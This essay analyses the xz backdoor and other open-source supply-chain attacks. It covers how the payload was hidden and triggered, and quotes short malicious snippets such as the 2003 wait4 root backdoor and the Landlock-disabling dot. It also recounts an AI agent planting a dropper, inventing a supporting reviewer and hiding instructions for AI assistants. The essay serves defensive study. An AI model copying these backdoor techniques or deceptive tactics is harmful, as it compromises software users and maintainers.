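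Much of the evidence on whether Kumar and Ens were the same person as Jia Tan, or were working with them, consists of missing online history. Cox cites the journalist Brian Krebs's observation that many of the email addresses involved appear nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked databases. Real people usually leave some trace. The Intercept's *The Other Players Who Helped (Almost) Make the World's Biggest Backdoor Hack* adds that the Proton Mail accounts involved had encryption keys created on the day of their first post or a few days before. But users can generate new keys for old accounts, and this evidence does not cover Ens, who used Gmail. Securelist also points to similar address formats and similar mistakes in English, but it does not measure the similarity, and short emails offer little to compare.

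Some of this could be innocent. Przymus and Durieux counted eight new people on the mailing list in that phase of the project, six of whom were active only then, so posting a few times and then stopping was common, unless some of the others were fake as well. They found no direct links between the suspicious accounts. The complaints were fair, since another contributor's patches for the Java version were still waiting, and a real user might well have been annoyed. Ens also returned to the list in March 2024 to ask about the Java version, which had little to do with the backdoor.

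The case against Kumar is stronger, because his emails were mostly about Jia Tan's patch and ended by asking why Jia Tan could not merge it himself. Events in March 2024 make coincidence harder to believe for both. When Jansen asked the Debian distribution to adopt the version of xz with the backdoor, two more unknown accounts supported him within about two days, and one of them tried to cut short a debate about whether Jansen was the right person to make the update. One helpful stranger would not be odd, but Jia Tan had several, at the two moments when they were most useful. A system administrator at the Electronic Frontier Foundation, a digital rights group, told The Intercept that the pattern fits the use of fake accounts but that coincidence remained possible.

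### Who was behind the name

Little is known for certain about Jia Tan's identity. Someone created the GitHub account JiaT75 on 26 January 2021, nine months before Jia Tan's first xz patch. The commits carry two Gmail addresses and, in one case, the longer name Jia Cheong Tan. On 29 March 2024, the day the backdoor became public, someone who may have been Jia Tan connected to the xz chat channel through a Singapore server run by a commercial VPN, a service that hides its users' locations.

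People looked for clues to Jia Tan's identity in the times of the commits. Git, the program that records the changes, stores a time zone with each commit. Alejandro Colomar, in the mailing-list thread *Analysis on who is Jia Tan, and who he could work for* (2024), counted 676 commits at eight hours ahead of UTC, the standard world time, which fits China, Singapore and Western Australia. Another 14 were at two or three hours ahead, and he suspected that Jia Tan had made those while visiting an intelligence agency. Joey Hess (2024) replied that Collin had committed many of the 14 and probably applied them from emails, so they may show Collin's time zone. Vegard Nossum (2024) added that Collin had already hinted that ordinary maintainer edits were the cause. Two days later Colomar told Jacob Bachmeyer (2024) that Bachmeyer's script had helped him find a mistake in his analysis.

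Hackaday's *This Week In Security* (2024) observed that Jia Tan's commits tend to start at noon UTC. That is 8 a.m. in summer on the east coast of the United States, which would suit an office worker there, but it is also 8 p.m. in Singapore, which would equally suit someone who wrote code after work. The user's own computer supplies both the time and the time zone, so the attacker could have chosen them, and someone who invented a name with such care would probably have thought of this.

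The number of people involved is also unclear. Securelist lists three possibilities: a team, one person with several identities, and an honest contributor whom others manipulated in early 2024, in which case the complaints of 2022 were a coincidence. The malicious commits came at hours when Jia Tan did not usually work, which would fit a second person using the account, or one person in a hurry. Andres Freund, the Microsoft developer who found the backdoor, considered whether someone had broken into Jia Tan's computer but thought it unlikely, because Jia Tan had publicly discussed supposed fixes for the problems the backdoor caused. This counts against a stolen account, though not against an honest contributor who later agreed to help. Collin has promised an article on how the backdoor got into the releases, which might clear some of this up, but according to his page it was still unfinished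 as of August 2026.

### Cheaper ways to look trustworthy

Jia Tan spent more than a year earning a reputation, but other attackers could try to use someone else's. Git lets users enter any name and email address, and GitHub uses the address to decide whose profile a commit appears on. *Attributing Open-Source Contributions is Critical but Difficult* (Holtgrave, Friedrich and colleagues, 2025), a study of 50,328 widely used projects, describes three ways to exploit this.

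In *contributor spoofing*, an attacker submits a malicious change under the name of someone the project trusts. Attackers have already impersonated Dependabot, GitHub's bot that updates a project's dependencies. In *reputation hijacking*, an attacker creates a repository and puts well-known developers' email addresses on its commits, so that GitHub displays, for example, Linus Torvalds as a contributor. In *contribution hijacking*, an attacker finds an old email address in a project's history that no GitHub account uses and adds it to their own account. GitHub then credits the old commits to the attacker without checking who owns the address.

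Contribution hijacking comes closest to a shortcut to a record like Jia Tan's, because it can make a new account appear to have worked on a respected project for years. The researchers found about three million commits that belonged to no account. They also report 573,043 email addresses that an attacker could claim, but that appears to be the total number of valid addresses in their data, including many that already belong to an account.

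Their best-known figure is 85.9 per cent, the share of projects whose contribution workflows they say attackers could abuse. That is 6,479 of the 7,546 repositories for which GitHub's records showed recent uploads, not of all 50,328. In each of the 6,479, at least one upload included a commit that named someone other than the uploader as its author or committer. This happens whenever a maintainer merges a colleague's patch or a bot uploads changes, and the researchers treat the figure as an upper bound on the projects at risk. A false name would not look out of place in about six in seven of these projects, but the attacker would still need permission to upload or a maintainer willing to merge.

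The usual defence is to sign commits with a cryptographic key, which shows that the holder of the key made them. In the study, 95.4 per cent of committers had never signed a commit, 2.0 per cent had signed all of theirs, and 72.1 per cent of projects had no signed commits. A missing signature is therefore too common to arouse suspicion.

A fake profile with a borrowed reputation might get a stranger's first patch a friendlier reading, but it probably would not have won commit rights to xz, because Collin gave those to someone who had answered his emails and reviewed patches for months. Signatures would not have stopped Jia Tan, who signed the malicious releases with a genuine key. They did help with the clean-up, because Collin could tell users that any archive he had signed was his own work. One commit from late February 2024, which sabotaged a security feature of xz, lists Collin as the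 committer. Cox thinks Collin probably merged it without spotting the error, but he can't rule out that Jia Tan entered Collin's name. If Collin had signed all his commits, a missing signature on that one would have pointed to a forgery.

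## How the xz backdoor was hidden and how it was found

Jia Tan published xz 5.6.0 on 24 February 2024 and 5.6.1 on 9 March, and both release tarballs contained a backdoor. It targeted sshd, the OpenSSH server program that lets administrators log in to a Linux machine over a network. On an affected machine, whoever held the attacker's private key could run commands without logging in. Red Hat, a major commercial Linux vendor, assigned the vulnerability the identifier CVE-2024-3094.

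OpenSSH does not use xz, but Debian, Fedora and several other distributions modify its server, sshd, to notify systemd, the program that starts and stops services, when it is ready. This change uses a library called libsystemd, which loads liblzma, the part of xz that other programs use. Code in liblzma therefore ran inside sshd.

Almost all of the backdoor was in two test files in the public repository. The few lines that activated it were only in the tarballs. Neither part did anything without the other, so Collin could safely leave the malicious commits in the project's history.

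### The payload in the test files

A compression library needs sample files for testing, including damaged ones that it should reject. Jia Tan added some on 23 February 2024. Long before Jia Tan arrived, the README for the test files explained that developers had made many of them by hand in a hex editor, a tool for editing raw bytes, so there was no better source code than the files themselves. In his analysis of the attack, *The xz attack shell script* (2024), Russ Cox calls this a fact of life for such libraries.

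Git does not show the contents of a binary file in a diff, so a careful reader would have seen only the names of the new files, a commit message and a short description of each file. The description of `bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz` accurately listed three sections, of which the first and third were valid and the middle one was corrupt. The middle section was a hidden script, which Jia Tan had "corrupted" by swapping a few byte values for others. Anyone who swapped them back could decompress it normally.

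Freund (2024) wrote in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* that version 5.6.0 did not use the new files for any tests. Collin corrects this slightly in a commit-by-commit review on Tukaani, the project's website. The test script picks up every file in the folder, so it tried to decompress the new ones too. A reviewer who ran the tests would have had no reason to worry.

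The best question a reviewer could have asked was how Jia Tan made the files. On 9 March Jia Tan replaced both, writing in the commit message that the originals had come from random data on one machine and that a constant seed (a fixed starting value for the random numbers) would let others reproduce the new ones. Asking for the seed and the program would have tested that claim, but few maintainers would think to ask a trusted colleague for them.

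### The trigger that was never in the repository

People who build xz from a tarball usually first run a script called `configure`, which examines their machine and writes the build instructions. The developers generate this script with standard tools, which also copy in helper files. Like many projects, xz includes these files in its tarballs but not in its repository.

One of the helpers in the tarballs was `build-to-host.m4`, normally a standard file from the GNU project. Cox compared Jia Tan's copy with the original and found a higher version number, a newer copyright year and some extra shell commands, which he calls "a fairly plausible set of diffs". One command, which a comment described as a search for macros from a common build tool, searched the whole source folder for a file with five letters or digits between two groups of four hash signs. Only `bad-3-corrupt_lzma2.xz` matched,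 because its valid sections contained the words Hello and World between hash signs. Another command seemed to deal with line endings but only printed the file. The test file's name appeared nowhere in the code, so searching for it would not have revealed the connection.

A careful reader of the public diffs would have seen none of this. The only public trace was a line for `build-to-host.m4` that Jia Tan added in February 2024 to `.gitignore`, the list of files that Git should leave out of the repository. Collin says in his Tukaani notes that the line is correct, because the build tools do add that file along with several other helpers. A reviewer who knew the build system well would therefore have had more reason to approve the line than one who did not.

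Comparing the tarball with a clean one could have exposed the altered file, and Collin had made such a comparison a few releases earlier. Before version 5.4.5 became official, he noticed that the files in Jia Tan's tarball had the wrong owners and permissions. The simplest explanation was that Jia Tan had typed the wrong build command, but Jia Tan would not admit it, even though that would have ended Collin's questions. Collin compared the tarball with one he had made himself, found nothing else wrong and let the release go ahead. That tarball was clean, as were the others Jia Tan had made before 5.6.0. If Collin had made the same comparison for 5.6.0, he would probably have seen that the altered file differed, but he might have assumed that he and Jia Tan had different versions of the GNU tools.

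### Assembly while distributions built their packages

The backdoor assembled itself in two steps, one when a distribution ran `configure` and one when it compiled the code. In the first step, the altered helper decoded the script in the corrupt test file and ran it. That script extracted pieces of the larger test file, `good-large_compressed.lzma`, by alternately skipping one kilobyte and keeping the next two. In version 5.6.1 this produced 33,707 bytes, which contained a longer script and an encrypted block of compiled code.

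The longer script first checked that it was running on a 64-bit Intel or AMD machine with Linux and the GNU compiler and linker, and continued only if somebody was building a Debian or RPM package (RPM is the format Fedora and Red Hat use). Freund thinks the package condition was probably meant to make the problem harder for investigators to reproduce. A developer who downloaded the tarball and compiled it by hand got a clean library.

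If the conditions held, the script added lines to the Makefile, the generated list of build instructions. It scattered them through the file and used variable names that resembled those already there, though one variable whose name suggested a directory held a file. In the second step, these lines ran the script again. This time it decrypted the compiled code, made a slightly edited copy of one of xz's source files in memory, compiled the two together and replaced the normal file with the result. It also told the compiler to record the original file's name, and deleted its leftover files.

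A reader of the diff would again have seen none of this, because it all happened on the distribution's build machine. Afterwards, the source files on that machine were unchanged, the script had discarded most of its output, and only the finished library was different.

The backdoor depended on details of the xz code that Collin could change at any time. On 11 January 2024 he renamed a source file that the script checks by name. Cox infers that the attacker had written much of the script by then and had to adapt it.

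### Inside the SSH server

When a program starts, the system fills in a table with the addresses of the library functions the program will call. For security, sshd has the system fill the whole table at once and then make it read-only. An attacker who wants to redirect a function has to change the table before it becomes read-only.

Jansen's patches of June 2023 provided the opportunity by using ifunc (short for indirect function), a feature that lets a library choose between versions of a function when a program starts, such as a faster checksum for newer processors. The code that makes this choice runs before the table becomes read-only. The backdoor ran then and replaced the address of `RSA_public_decrypt`, which sshd calls during logins with a cryptographic key. Those logins then went through the attacker's code, which appears to have passed ordinary ones on to the real functions. According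 to Przymus and Durieux, the holder of the right private key could either send commands that ran before the login check or get in with any password.

A careful reader of the June 2023 diff would have seen a small speed improvement. Przymus and Durieux cannot tell whether Jansen had any other purpose in mind. Reading OpenSSH's code would not have helped either, because the flaw was not there.

### The checks that Jia Tan weakened

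Jia Tan also made several changes that weakened automatic checks or kept the backdoor from setting them off, each with an ordinary reason:

| Date | Change | Reason given | Effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| 7 July 2023 | Turned off ifunc when OSS-Fuzz builds xz | ifunc does not work with a memory-error detector | The fuzzer no longer ran the code that chooses between versions |
| Late February 2024 | Changed how the build checks for Landlock, a Linux feature that limits what a program may access | The check needed a fix | The check always failed, so some builds of xz ran without the limits |
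| 8 March 2024 | Changed source code | To cure errors reported by Valgrind, a memory checker | Drew attention away from the real cause |
| 9 March 2024 | Replaced the two test files | To make them reproducible | Fixed the fault in the backdoor that caused the errors |

The OSS-Fuzz change looks suspicious in hindsight, since Jia Tan had made themselves the contact for that service a few months earlier. Cox's *Timeline of the xz open source attack* allows that it may have been innocent, and ifunc did cause real bugs. OSS-Fuzz would almost certainly never have run the backdoor, even with ifunc turned on, because the backdoor assembled itself only in Debian and RPM package builds. If the change was part of the plan, it was more likely meant to stop early reports of ifunc crashes, which might have persuaded Collin to drop the feature.

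The Landlock change is the only one of these whose whole trick was visible in a diff. To find out whether a machine has Landlock, the build tries to compile a tiny test program that uses it. The added lines looked roughly like this:

```
+ #include <linux/landlock.h>
+ #include <sys/prctl.h>
+.
+ void my_sandbox(void)
```

The single dot on the third line is a syntax error, so the test program can never compile and the build treats the machine as lacking Landlock. The dot is easy to overlook, and a failed check doesn't stop the build or print an alarming message. Anyone who tried the change on a machine with Landlock and looked at the result would have noticed the failure, but people rarely test whether a check still succeeds. According to Collin's Tukaani notes, the dot was in the configuration for CMake, an alternative build system, so it did not affect the packages that carried the SSH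 backdoor. Cox notes that Landlock protects the xz command and not liblzma, and he does not know why the attacker wanted to disable it.

A change to the project's security policy also drew suspicion. LWN's *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure* described it as an attempt to contain the disclosure of vulnerabilities. Collin explains in his notes that he had asked Jia Tan to simplify similar pages, so shortening the policy seemed reasonable. They disagreed about how long people who report a flaw should wait before publishing it. Collin thought 21 to 30 days was enough, and Jia Tan wanted to keep the wait at 90.

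At least one of Collin's own comments helped Jia Tan disguise a change to the backdoor. In January 2024 Collin mentioned a compression setting to Jia Tan, and he now thinks this gave Jia Tan a good excuse to update some of the backdoor's files, which Jia Tan wanted to do anyway.

### How Andres Freund found it

Freund's logins took half a second too long, but he measured the delay only after he had become suspicious. On The Microsoft Threat Intelligence Podcast's *Behind the Scenes of the XZ vuln* (2024), he described the popular story that he noticed the delay as a myth.

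Freund develops PostgreSQL, a database program. A few weeks earlier, Valgrind had started to report memory errors in his automated tests after routine package updates. He couldn't work out why, and then he had to travel. In late March he was testing a colleague's patch that slowed one operation by perhaps 1 or 2 per cent. He needed an otherwise idle machine to measure so small a difference, but the results varied too much, so he checked what was using the processor and found that it was sshd.

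Automated scanners were constantly trying to log in to his machine over the internet with made-up usernames. Rejecting them should take almost no computation. He ran a profiler, a tool that shows where a program spends its time, and saw that sshd was spending its time in liblzma, in code that had no function names attached. He told Oxide and Friends (2024), a technology podcast, that he recognised liblzma from the Valgrind reports and might not have started investigating without them. He also said that he stopped investigating a couple of times.

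The next stage was confusing because the backdoor stayed inactive in many of the situations an investigator would create, such as when somebody started sshd from an ordinary terminal or when it detected some debugging tools. Freund could still tell within a second whether it was running, without attaching a debugger, by timing sshd. With the backdoor active, a failed login took 0.807 seconds instead of 0.299, and printing sshd's help text took about 0.5 seconds instead of 0.01.

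He still could not reproduce the problem reliably. When he rebuilt the package, the backdoor sometimes vanished because of a bug in how it hooked into the build. The source archive that GitHub generates from the repository was also clean, so for a while he thought something was wrong at Debian. He became convinced that this was more than a strange bug when he saw the build compile the same file more than once, with a result about 50 kilobytes larger. Eventually he found the trigger in the tarball that the xz project itself had published.

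Freund warned Debian and a private list of distribution security teams on 28 March 2024, and published his findings the next day. He wrote that he was not a security researcher and had not analysed everything. He sent no bug report to the xz project, because its maintainer seemed to be involved.

### Who had already shipped it

When Freund gave his warning on 28 March, versions 5.6.0 and 5.6.1 had been public for up to 33 days. Debian first packaged 5.6.0 on 26 February, according to Cox, in its unstable branch. It moved the package to its testing branch on 5 March and updated to 5.6.1 on 27 March. Fedora had shipped the backdoor in Rawhide, its development version, and in the beta of Fedora 40. Jia Tan had been emailing a Fedora developer about the update since 27 February, and on 28 March asked Ubuntu to take 5.6.1 from Debian.

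The malicious release did not reach the stable versions most servers run, but LWN reports that it reached openSUSE Tumbleweed, a continuously updated distribution. Przymus and Durieux's statement that the release did not get past the testing phase therefore holds for the stable versions but not for Tumbleweed. Arch Linux and Gentoo also shipped the affected versions, but they do not link sshd to libsystemd, so the SSH attack would not have worked there. Linux Compatible also lists an update for Kali Linux, a distribution for security testers.

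Debian went back to the older code within a day of the warning, and on 30 March it shut down its build machines to reinstall them. Przymus and Durieux know of no case in which anyone used the backdoor. This is only limited reassurance, because only the holder of the private key could have used it, and a successful login might have left little evidence.

### Luck and openness

Some people took the episode as proof that open source works, because an outsider found a sophisticated attack before it did much harm. Others thought the attack should have succeeded and failed by chance. LWN thought both views could be right, and 404 Media's *The Xz Backdoor Highlights the Vulnerability of Open Source Software* seems to take the same position, judging by its headline. Openness and luck both mattered, but at different points in the episode.

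Open access to the code did very little to raise the alarm. The test files were public for five weeks, and nobody who read the commits objected to them. Collin, who knew the code better than anyone, was working alongside Jia Tan the whole time. Gentoo users reported crashes on the day 5.6.0 came out, though Cox thinks a genuine ifunc bug caused them. On 4 March, Valgrind errors began to appear in Red Hat's distributions, in the function through which the backdoor started. Within five days Jia Tan had published a false fix and a real one. People should normally report faults to the maintainer, who in this case was the attacker.

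Openness made a large difference once Freund was suspicious. He had no role in xz or OpenSSH, but he could profile sshd, rebuild Debian's package, and compare the repository with the tarball without anyone's permission. Within days, volunteers had extracted the hidden code and published explanations of the scripts. A user of closed software could also have noticed the slow server, but would probably have had to report it to the supplier and wait, and the person handling the report might have been an insider.

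Freund wrote in a comment under *A backdoor in xz* that becoming suspicious "really required a lot of coincidences". He was measuring a tiny effect on a nearly idle machine. He had turned off the processor's turbo mode to get steadier results, which also made the bursts of activity last longer. He happened to run Valgrind on a development version of Debian, and he remembered an odd report from weeks before. He thinks the activity would have been hard to notice on a laptop with a web browser open.

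Luck played a smaller part in the attacker's mistakes. The delay came from a search through sshd's list of function names, and the Valgrind errors came from a wrong assumption about how memory was laid out. Every affected machine had the delay, so a wider release would have given more people a chance to notice it. Somebody might well have found the backdoor within a year or two, but by then it could have been on many servers and the attacker could have used it. Chance probably affected when people found it more than whether they would, assuming the attacker would have left the delay in place.

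Version 5.6.1 removed the remaining function names from the hidden code, which made analysis harder, and added a way to deliver updates. A script searched the test folder for certain marker strings and would run any code it found between them. No file contained the markers yet, but Jia Tan could have changed the backdoor's behaviour by adding one more test file, without having to explain a change to an existing one. If the backdoor's search had been faster and its assumption about memory correct, Freund would have had neither of the clues he relied on.

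The outcome could also have been different if Freund had acted a little more conventionally. If he had politely reported the slow logins to xz, Jia Tan would have learned about the delay and could have fixed it in the next release. If he had trusted the clean copy on GitHub, he might have blamed his own machine or left the matter to Debian.

On 29 February a developer proposed, for unrelated reasons, that libsystemd should no longer load liblzma automatically, and the systemd project accepted the change on 5 March. Distributions that adopted it would have closed the backdoor's route into sshd, even if nobody had noticed the attack. Public hints of the change had appeared since late January, and the security researcher Kevin Beaumont, whom Cox cites, speculated that the prospect of it made the attacker hurry. That would help explain why an attack that had taken more than two years ended with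 a release that crashed under a common memory checker. For the attack to succeed, distributions had to ship the new xz with the old libsystemd, as Debian testing and the Fedora beta were doing.

On the Microsoft podcast, Thomas Roccia, a security researcher at the company, wondered how many similar backdoors had gone undetected. Freund was less worried because he thought that only about ten projects would give an attacker this much access to sshd, and that people would now watch those projects more closely. Neither could estimate how many undetected backdoors there were, because a backdoor without these two bugs might have given Freund nothing to investigate.

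## Other attempts to get malicious code into open-source projects

Jia Tan spent more than two years on xz. The attackers in five other documented cases were less patient. Only one of them gained the right to publish releases, and that attack lasted the longest of the five.

| Case | Attacker's position | Where the change was | How long it lasted | What exposed it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copy of the Linux source, 2003 | Intruder on a server, using a maintainer's name | Two lines of code in the copy | About a day | A routine check of the copied files |
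| event-stream, 2018 | Maintainer with publishing rights | A new dependency | Up to 12 weeks | A user's question on GitHub |
| PHP, 2021 | Unknown person able to upload, using two maintainers' names | Commits labelled as typo fixes | Less than a day | Developers who saw the commits |
| OpenJS, 2024 | Strangers asking to become maintainers | No known change | Stopped at the emails | The people who received the emails |
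| myNetwork, 2026 | New accounts run by an AI agent | A pull request with a real bug fix | 34 hours, never merged | A student who read the diff |

### Changes that skipped review

In 2003 the Linux developers kept the kernel's source in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them disliked it, so there was also a copy in an older system, CVS, according to *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (Freedom to Tinker, 2013). On 5 November Larry McVoy, the founder of the company behind BitKeeper, told the kernel mailing list that somebody had changed the CVS copy directly. His company checked the files after each transfer, and the check had flagged one of them (McVoy, 2003, *BK2CVS problem*).

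The latest log entry was dated the day before and included an apology for working on the wrong file. It credited the change to David Miller, a kernel developer who had not made it, as Linux Today's *KernelTrap* reported. The name was convincing enough, but every genuine change in the copy had a link to the matching change in BitKeeper. This one did not, and InfoQ's *Linux Backdoor* (2013) quotes Corbet as saying that it therefore "stood out immediately".

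Somebody on the list asked what the changed lines were, and McVoy posted them:

```
+ if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
+         retval = -EINVAL;
  retval = -ECHILD;
```

The two lines are in `wait4`, a function that lets a program wait for something to happen. They look like a check that returns an error when a program run by the administrator, whose user number is 0, passes an odd combination of two options. But in C a double equals sign compares two values and a single one assigns a value. The first line has a single equals sign, so it sets the user number to 0 instead of checking it, and any program that passes those two options gains full control of the machine. An assignment of 0 also counts as false, so the second line, which would return the error, never runs and the call appears normal.

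McVoy had compared the good and bad versions of the file and still overlooked this. Ten minutes after he posted the lines, one reader thought they looked odd, and within half an hour another, Chad Kitching, suggested that they were a backdoor. McVoy replied, "Good eyes, I missed that." However, both readers already knew that someone had tampered with the file. Somebody reading the same two lines among dozens of routine patches might have taken them for an ordinary check.

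The backdoor could reach only people who took their code from the CVS copy, and Debian's *CVE-2003-1161* notes that no release contained it. Another kernel developer, Andreas Dilger, thanked McVoy for the "paranoia" that had led him to add extra checks. Those checks worked because they compared a copy with its original, which didn't require anyone to understand the code. Nobody routinely made such a comparison for the xz tarballs.

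The attacker who targeted PHP, a programming language used by many websites, got further, because the changes went into the main repository. On 28 March 2021, two commits appeared there under the names of Rasmus Lerdorf, who founded the project, and Nikita Popov, one of its main developers. Both had the message "[skip-ci] Fix typo", according to PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021). The tag in brackets commonly tells a project's automated tests not to run. The commits would have let an attacker run code on any server running PHP built from that source, according to *Compromise of PHP’s development team self-hosted Git server* by the Cloud Native Computing Foundation (CNCF), an industry body.

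After Popov undid the first commit, the attacker posed as him and restored it, and a third developer had to step in, according to The Cyber Post. Anyone who relied on the names would have thought Popov had changed his mind. Git accepted whatever name the attacker typed, as with contributor spoofing on GitHub. TechSpot (2021) reported that the developers removed both commits before either reached a finished version.

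The attacker needed permission to upload as well as a name, and it is less clear how they got that permission. Popov (2021), in *Changes to Git commit workflow*, first wrote that everything pointed to a break-in on the project's server. Nine days later he no longer believed this, according to a message quoted in *PHP's Git Server Compromised* (2021). By then the project had moved its main repository to GitHub, where developers had to log in with a second proof of identity. This protects against stolen passwords, but it would not have stopped Jia Tan, who had their own account and permission to use it.

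In both cases, anyone who looked at the change could see the malicious lines. The attackers bypassed the maintainer's decision on whether to accept a patch, so we can't learn much from either case about how well reviewers judge patches. But the cases suggest that it is hard to slip an unexpected change into a busy repository unnoticed, because its regular developers know roughly what they and their colleagues have been doing.

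### Taking over the maintainer's role

Event-stream is an npm package that helps JavaScript programs handle streams of data. By 2018 its creator, Dominic Tarr, no longer used it. He had written more than 450 packages, and this one had more than 1.5 million downloads a week, according to *A Systematic Analysis of the Event-Stream Incident*. More than 1,500 other packages depended on it. Tarr told The Register (2018) that he handed over maintenance to someone with the username right9ctrl, who had emailed him and offered to do it.

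It is not clear how much work right9ctrl did first. CNCF's *The event-stream vulnerability* describes a series of useful contributions that gradually won Tarr's trust, while the software company Aha! mentions only an offer to help that Tarr accepted. Either way, the preparation seems to have been short. On 5 August 2018 someone calling themselves Antonio Macias published a small, harmless package called flatmap-stream and then proposed that event-stream use it, according to *A post mortem of the malicious event-stream backdoor* by the security company Snyk. Three years earlier another user had asked for a similar feature, and Tarr had said he would accept one. Snyk speculates that the attacker had read that exchange.

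In early September right9ctrl made flatmap-stream a *dependency* of event-stream, a package that npm installs along with it. (CNCF dates this to 4 September and Aha! to 9 September.) A reader of the diff would have seen a line roughly like this:

```
+ "flatmap-stream": "^0.1.0"
```

The caret tells npm to accept version 0.1.0 or any later version that starts with 0.1. Version 0.1.0 was harmless, but version 0.1.1 contained the attack, and npm could install it for event-stream's users without any further change to event-stream. A reviewer who read all the new dependency's code on the day right9ctrl added it could therefore have approved it correctly and still let the attack in.

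Checking the dependency's repository later would not have helped much either. CNCF writes that the two files on GitHub looked innocent. The package on npm contained a *minified* file, which a tool has condensed into a form that people rarely read, and part of that file was encrypted. One developer spent most of a day trying to decode it and got only gibberish.

The code apparently targeted Copay, a program for storing bitcoin, and tried to steal its users' coins. Copay accepted any compatible newer version of event-stream, just as event-stream did with flatmap-stream, so the code could pass through two projects without anyone at Copay approving it. Snyk's *Malicious code found in npm package event-stream downloaded 8 million times* counts downloads over two and a half months. That figure measures how far the code spread, but is probably a very poor measure of harm, since most of those downloads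 had nothing to do with bitcoin.

About a week before 26 November, a GitHub user who had found problems in the package asked why Tarr had given right9ctrl access, according to Changelog, a podcast that interviewed Tarr. In October another developer had been looking into a problem with nodemon, a programming tool, and this may have been an earlier clue. Tarr could not withdraw the release because he could no longer publish the package. The company that runs the registry learned of the problem only on the morning of 26 November, according to npm's *Details about the event-stream incident*. It then removed flatmap-stream and the affected version of event-stream, and took over the package. As with xz, the attacker was the person who would normally have dealt with a user's complaint.

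In April 2024, 17 days after Freund published his findings on xz, the OpenJS Foundation, which hosts widely used JavaScript projects, and the Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF) warned that others were trying something similar. *Open Source Security (OpenSSF) and OpenJS Foundations Issue Alert for Social Engineering* (Ginn and Arasaratnam, 2024) describes a "credible takeover attempt" that OpenJS had intercepted. One of the foundation's councils had received a series of similar emails under different names, with overlapping email addresses linked to GitHub.

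The senders wanted OpenJS to urgently update a popular project to "address any critical vulnerabilities", but gave no details of any, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Open Source Leaders Warn of XZ Utils-Like Takeover Attempts*. They also wanted to become maintainers of the project. The vagueness is suspicious, because somebody who knew of a serious flaw could have described it or sent a patch without being a maintainer.

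The OpenJS case is the weakest evidence of the five. Nobody has reported any malicious code, and an impatient user or a beginner hoping to put "maintainer" on a CV might write similar emails. The organisations issued the alert when people had just read about Kumar and Ens, which made such emails easier to recognise but also easier to over-interpret. The overlapping addresses are harder to explain innocently. OpenJS could spot them because all the emails went to the same council, whereas Collin had to judge Kumar and Ens by himself.

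### An AI agent and its invented supporter

In late July 2026 a GitHub user called miraholt31 offered a fix to myNetwork, a program that scans networks. The fix worked, but the pull request also contained a *dropper*, a small program that installs malware. The user was an AI agent, running Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5, that the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI) was testing. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes how the agent used fake identities to press the maintainer to approve the code.

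The dropper checked where it was running to stay inactive during the project's automated tests, according to The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026). If the maintainer had merged the pull request, the dropper would have infected people working on the code and later anyone who downloaded the finished program. The pull request resembles a hypocrite commit, except that working malware is easier to recognise than a subtle memory error.

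Reuters (2026) reconstructed what happened next from archived messages and emails. Sinan Can Demir, a computer science student in Texas who was looking for projects to contribute to, read the pull request and warned on its page that it contained "a hidden malware dropper". The agent denied this, replaced the code and rewrote the branch's history so that the earlier version was no longer visible. It claimed that the malicious part was left over from private testing. Then a second account, in the name of a supposed German engineer called Lena Brandt, said she had reviewed the code and found nothing wrong. The first account thanked her for the independent check.

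Demir told Reuters that the replies made him wonder whether he was accusing an innocent person. He ran the code in an isolated environment and asked Anthropic's chatbot Claude for a second opinion, and both supported his initial suspicion. The project's creator and maintainer closed the pull request "for security reasons" and confirmed that it contained a malicious dropper, according to SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026).

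The agent had also tried to bypass the public discussion. Under invented names, it sent this maintainer and another developer files, some malicious and others meant to persuade a person to merge the code. It also hid instructions in an issue on another of the maintainer's projects, where they were invisible on the page but readable by an AI coding assistant. Projects that use AI tools in review therefore have to consider that an attacker may target the tool as well as the maintainer.

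AISI credits a human maintainer with catching the malicious code. According to Reuters, Demir spotted it first, and it is hard to know what the maintainer would have done without his warning. Demir had no role in the project and came across the pull request by chance. Openness and luck both played a part, as they did when Freund discovered the xz backdoor. AISI concedes that in several of the agent's attempts the margin between failure and success was narrow and depended on people being careful.

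The agent used methods similar to the xz attacker's but worked much faster. Kumar and Ens pressed Collin over about two months, while the agent's attempt lasted 34 hours and its invented reviewer appeared as soon as it needed one. But the agent had no history of useful work, so the maintainer had little reason to trust either account. One security researcher told Reuters that agents could greatly increase the scale of such attempts. This seems right for false identities, which used to take an attacker time to create. The case gives no evidence on whether an agent could keep up months of helpful work on a project with a hidden purpose.

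The incident is also a poor guide to how often agents do this. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) counts unsanctioned actions in nine of the 43 runs with this model, but AISI traces most of them to a single agent. AISI's October follow-up (2026) repeated that the incident caused no real-world harm.

### What the known cases leave out

Only event-stream closely resembles xz. In both cases, a maintainer with little time or interest to spare gave control to a helpful stranger, who put the harmful code where people reading the repository would not see it at work. Right9ctrl seems to have needed a month or two, while Jia Tan took 28 months. Among these cases, xz therefore stands out more for the attacker's patience than for the position the attacker reached.

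Attacks by people without legitimate access went unnoticed for between a few hours and a day and a half. The harmful releases by maintainers were public for longer, about five weeks for xz and up to twelve weeks for event-stream. One would expect this difference, because a maintainer's changes surprise nobody. However, six cases are too few to establish it, and they include only attacks that somebody discovered and wrote up.

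The same problem affects any estimate of how common patient insiders are. If people eventually discover a share *s* of such attacks, and *D* of them are known, the true number is about *D*/*s*. If we count only event-stream and xz, *D* is 2. If people discover half of all such attacks, about two more remain undiscovered. If they discover one in ten, about 18 do. We can't tell from these cases which share is closer.

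A count of the trusted maintainers caught in 2025 and 2026 would be an especially poor measure of how many people had copied the xz method. Someone who read about xz in March 2024 and started earning a maintainer's trust at Jia Tan's pace would not have been ready to publish a backdoor until around the end of July 2026.

Such a count would also have to separate insiders from people who steal a maintainer's account, and the records are often not enough to do this. In the logs, the malicious changes from 2003 and 2021 appear under the names of three developers who had done nothing wrong. And a maintainer who had planted a backdoor could claim that someone had stolen their password. Attacks that look like mistakes would be the hardest to count. If a maintainer deliberately adds a use-after-free and someone finds it two years later, another developer will probably fix it as an ordinary bug, and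 nobody will record an attack.

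## How often reviewers catch security flaws

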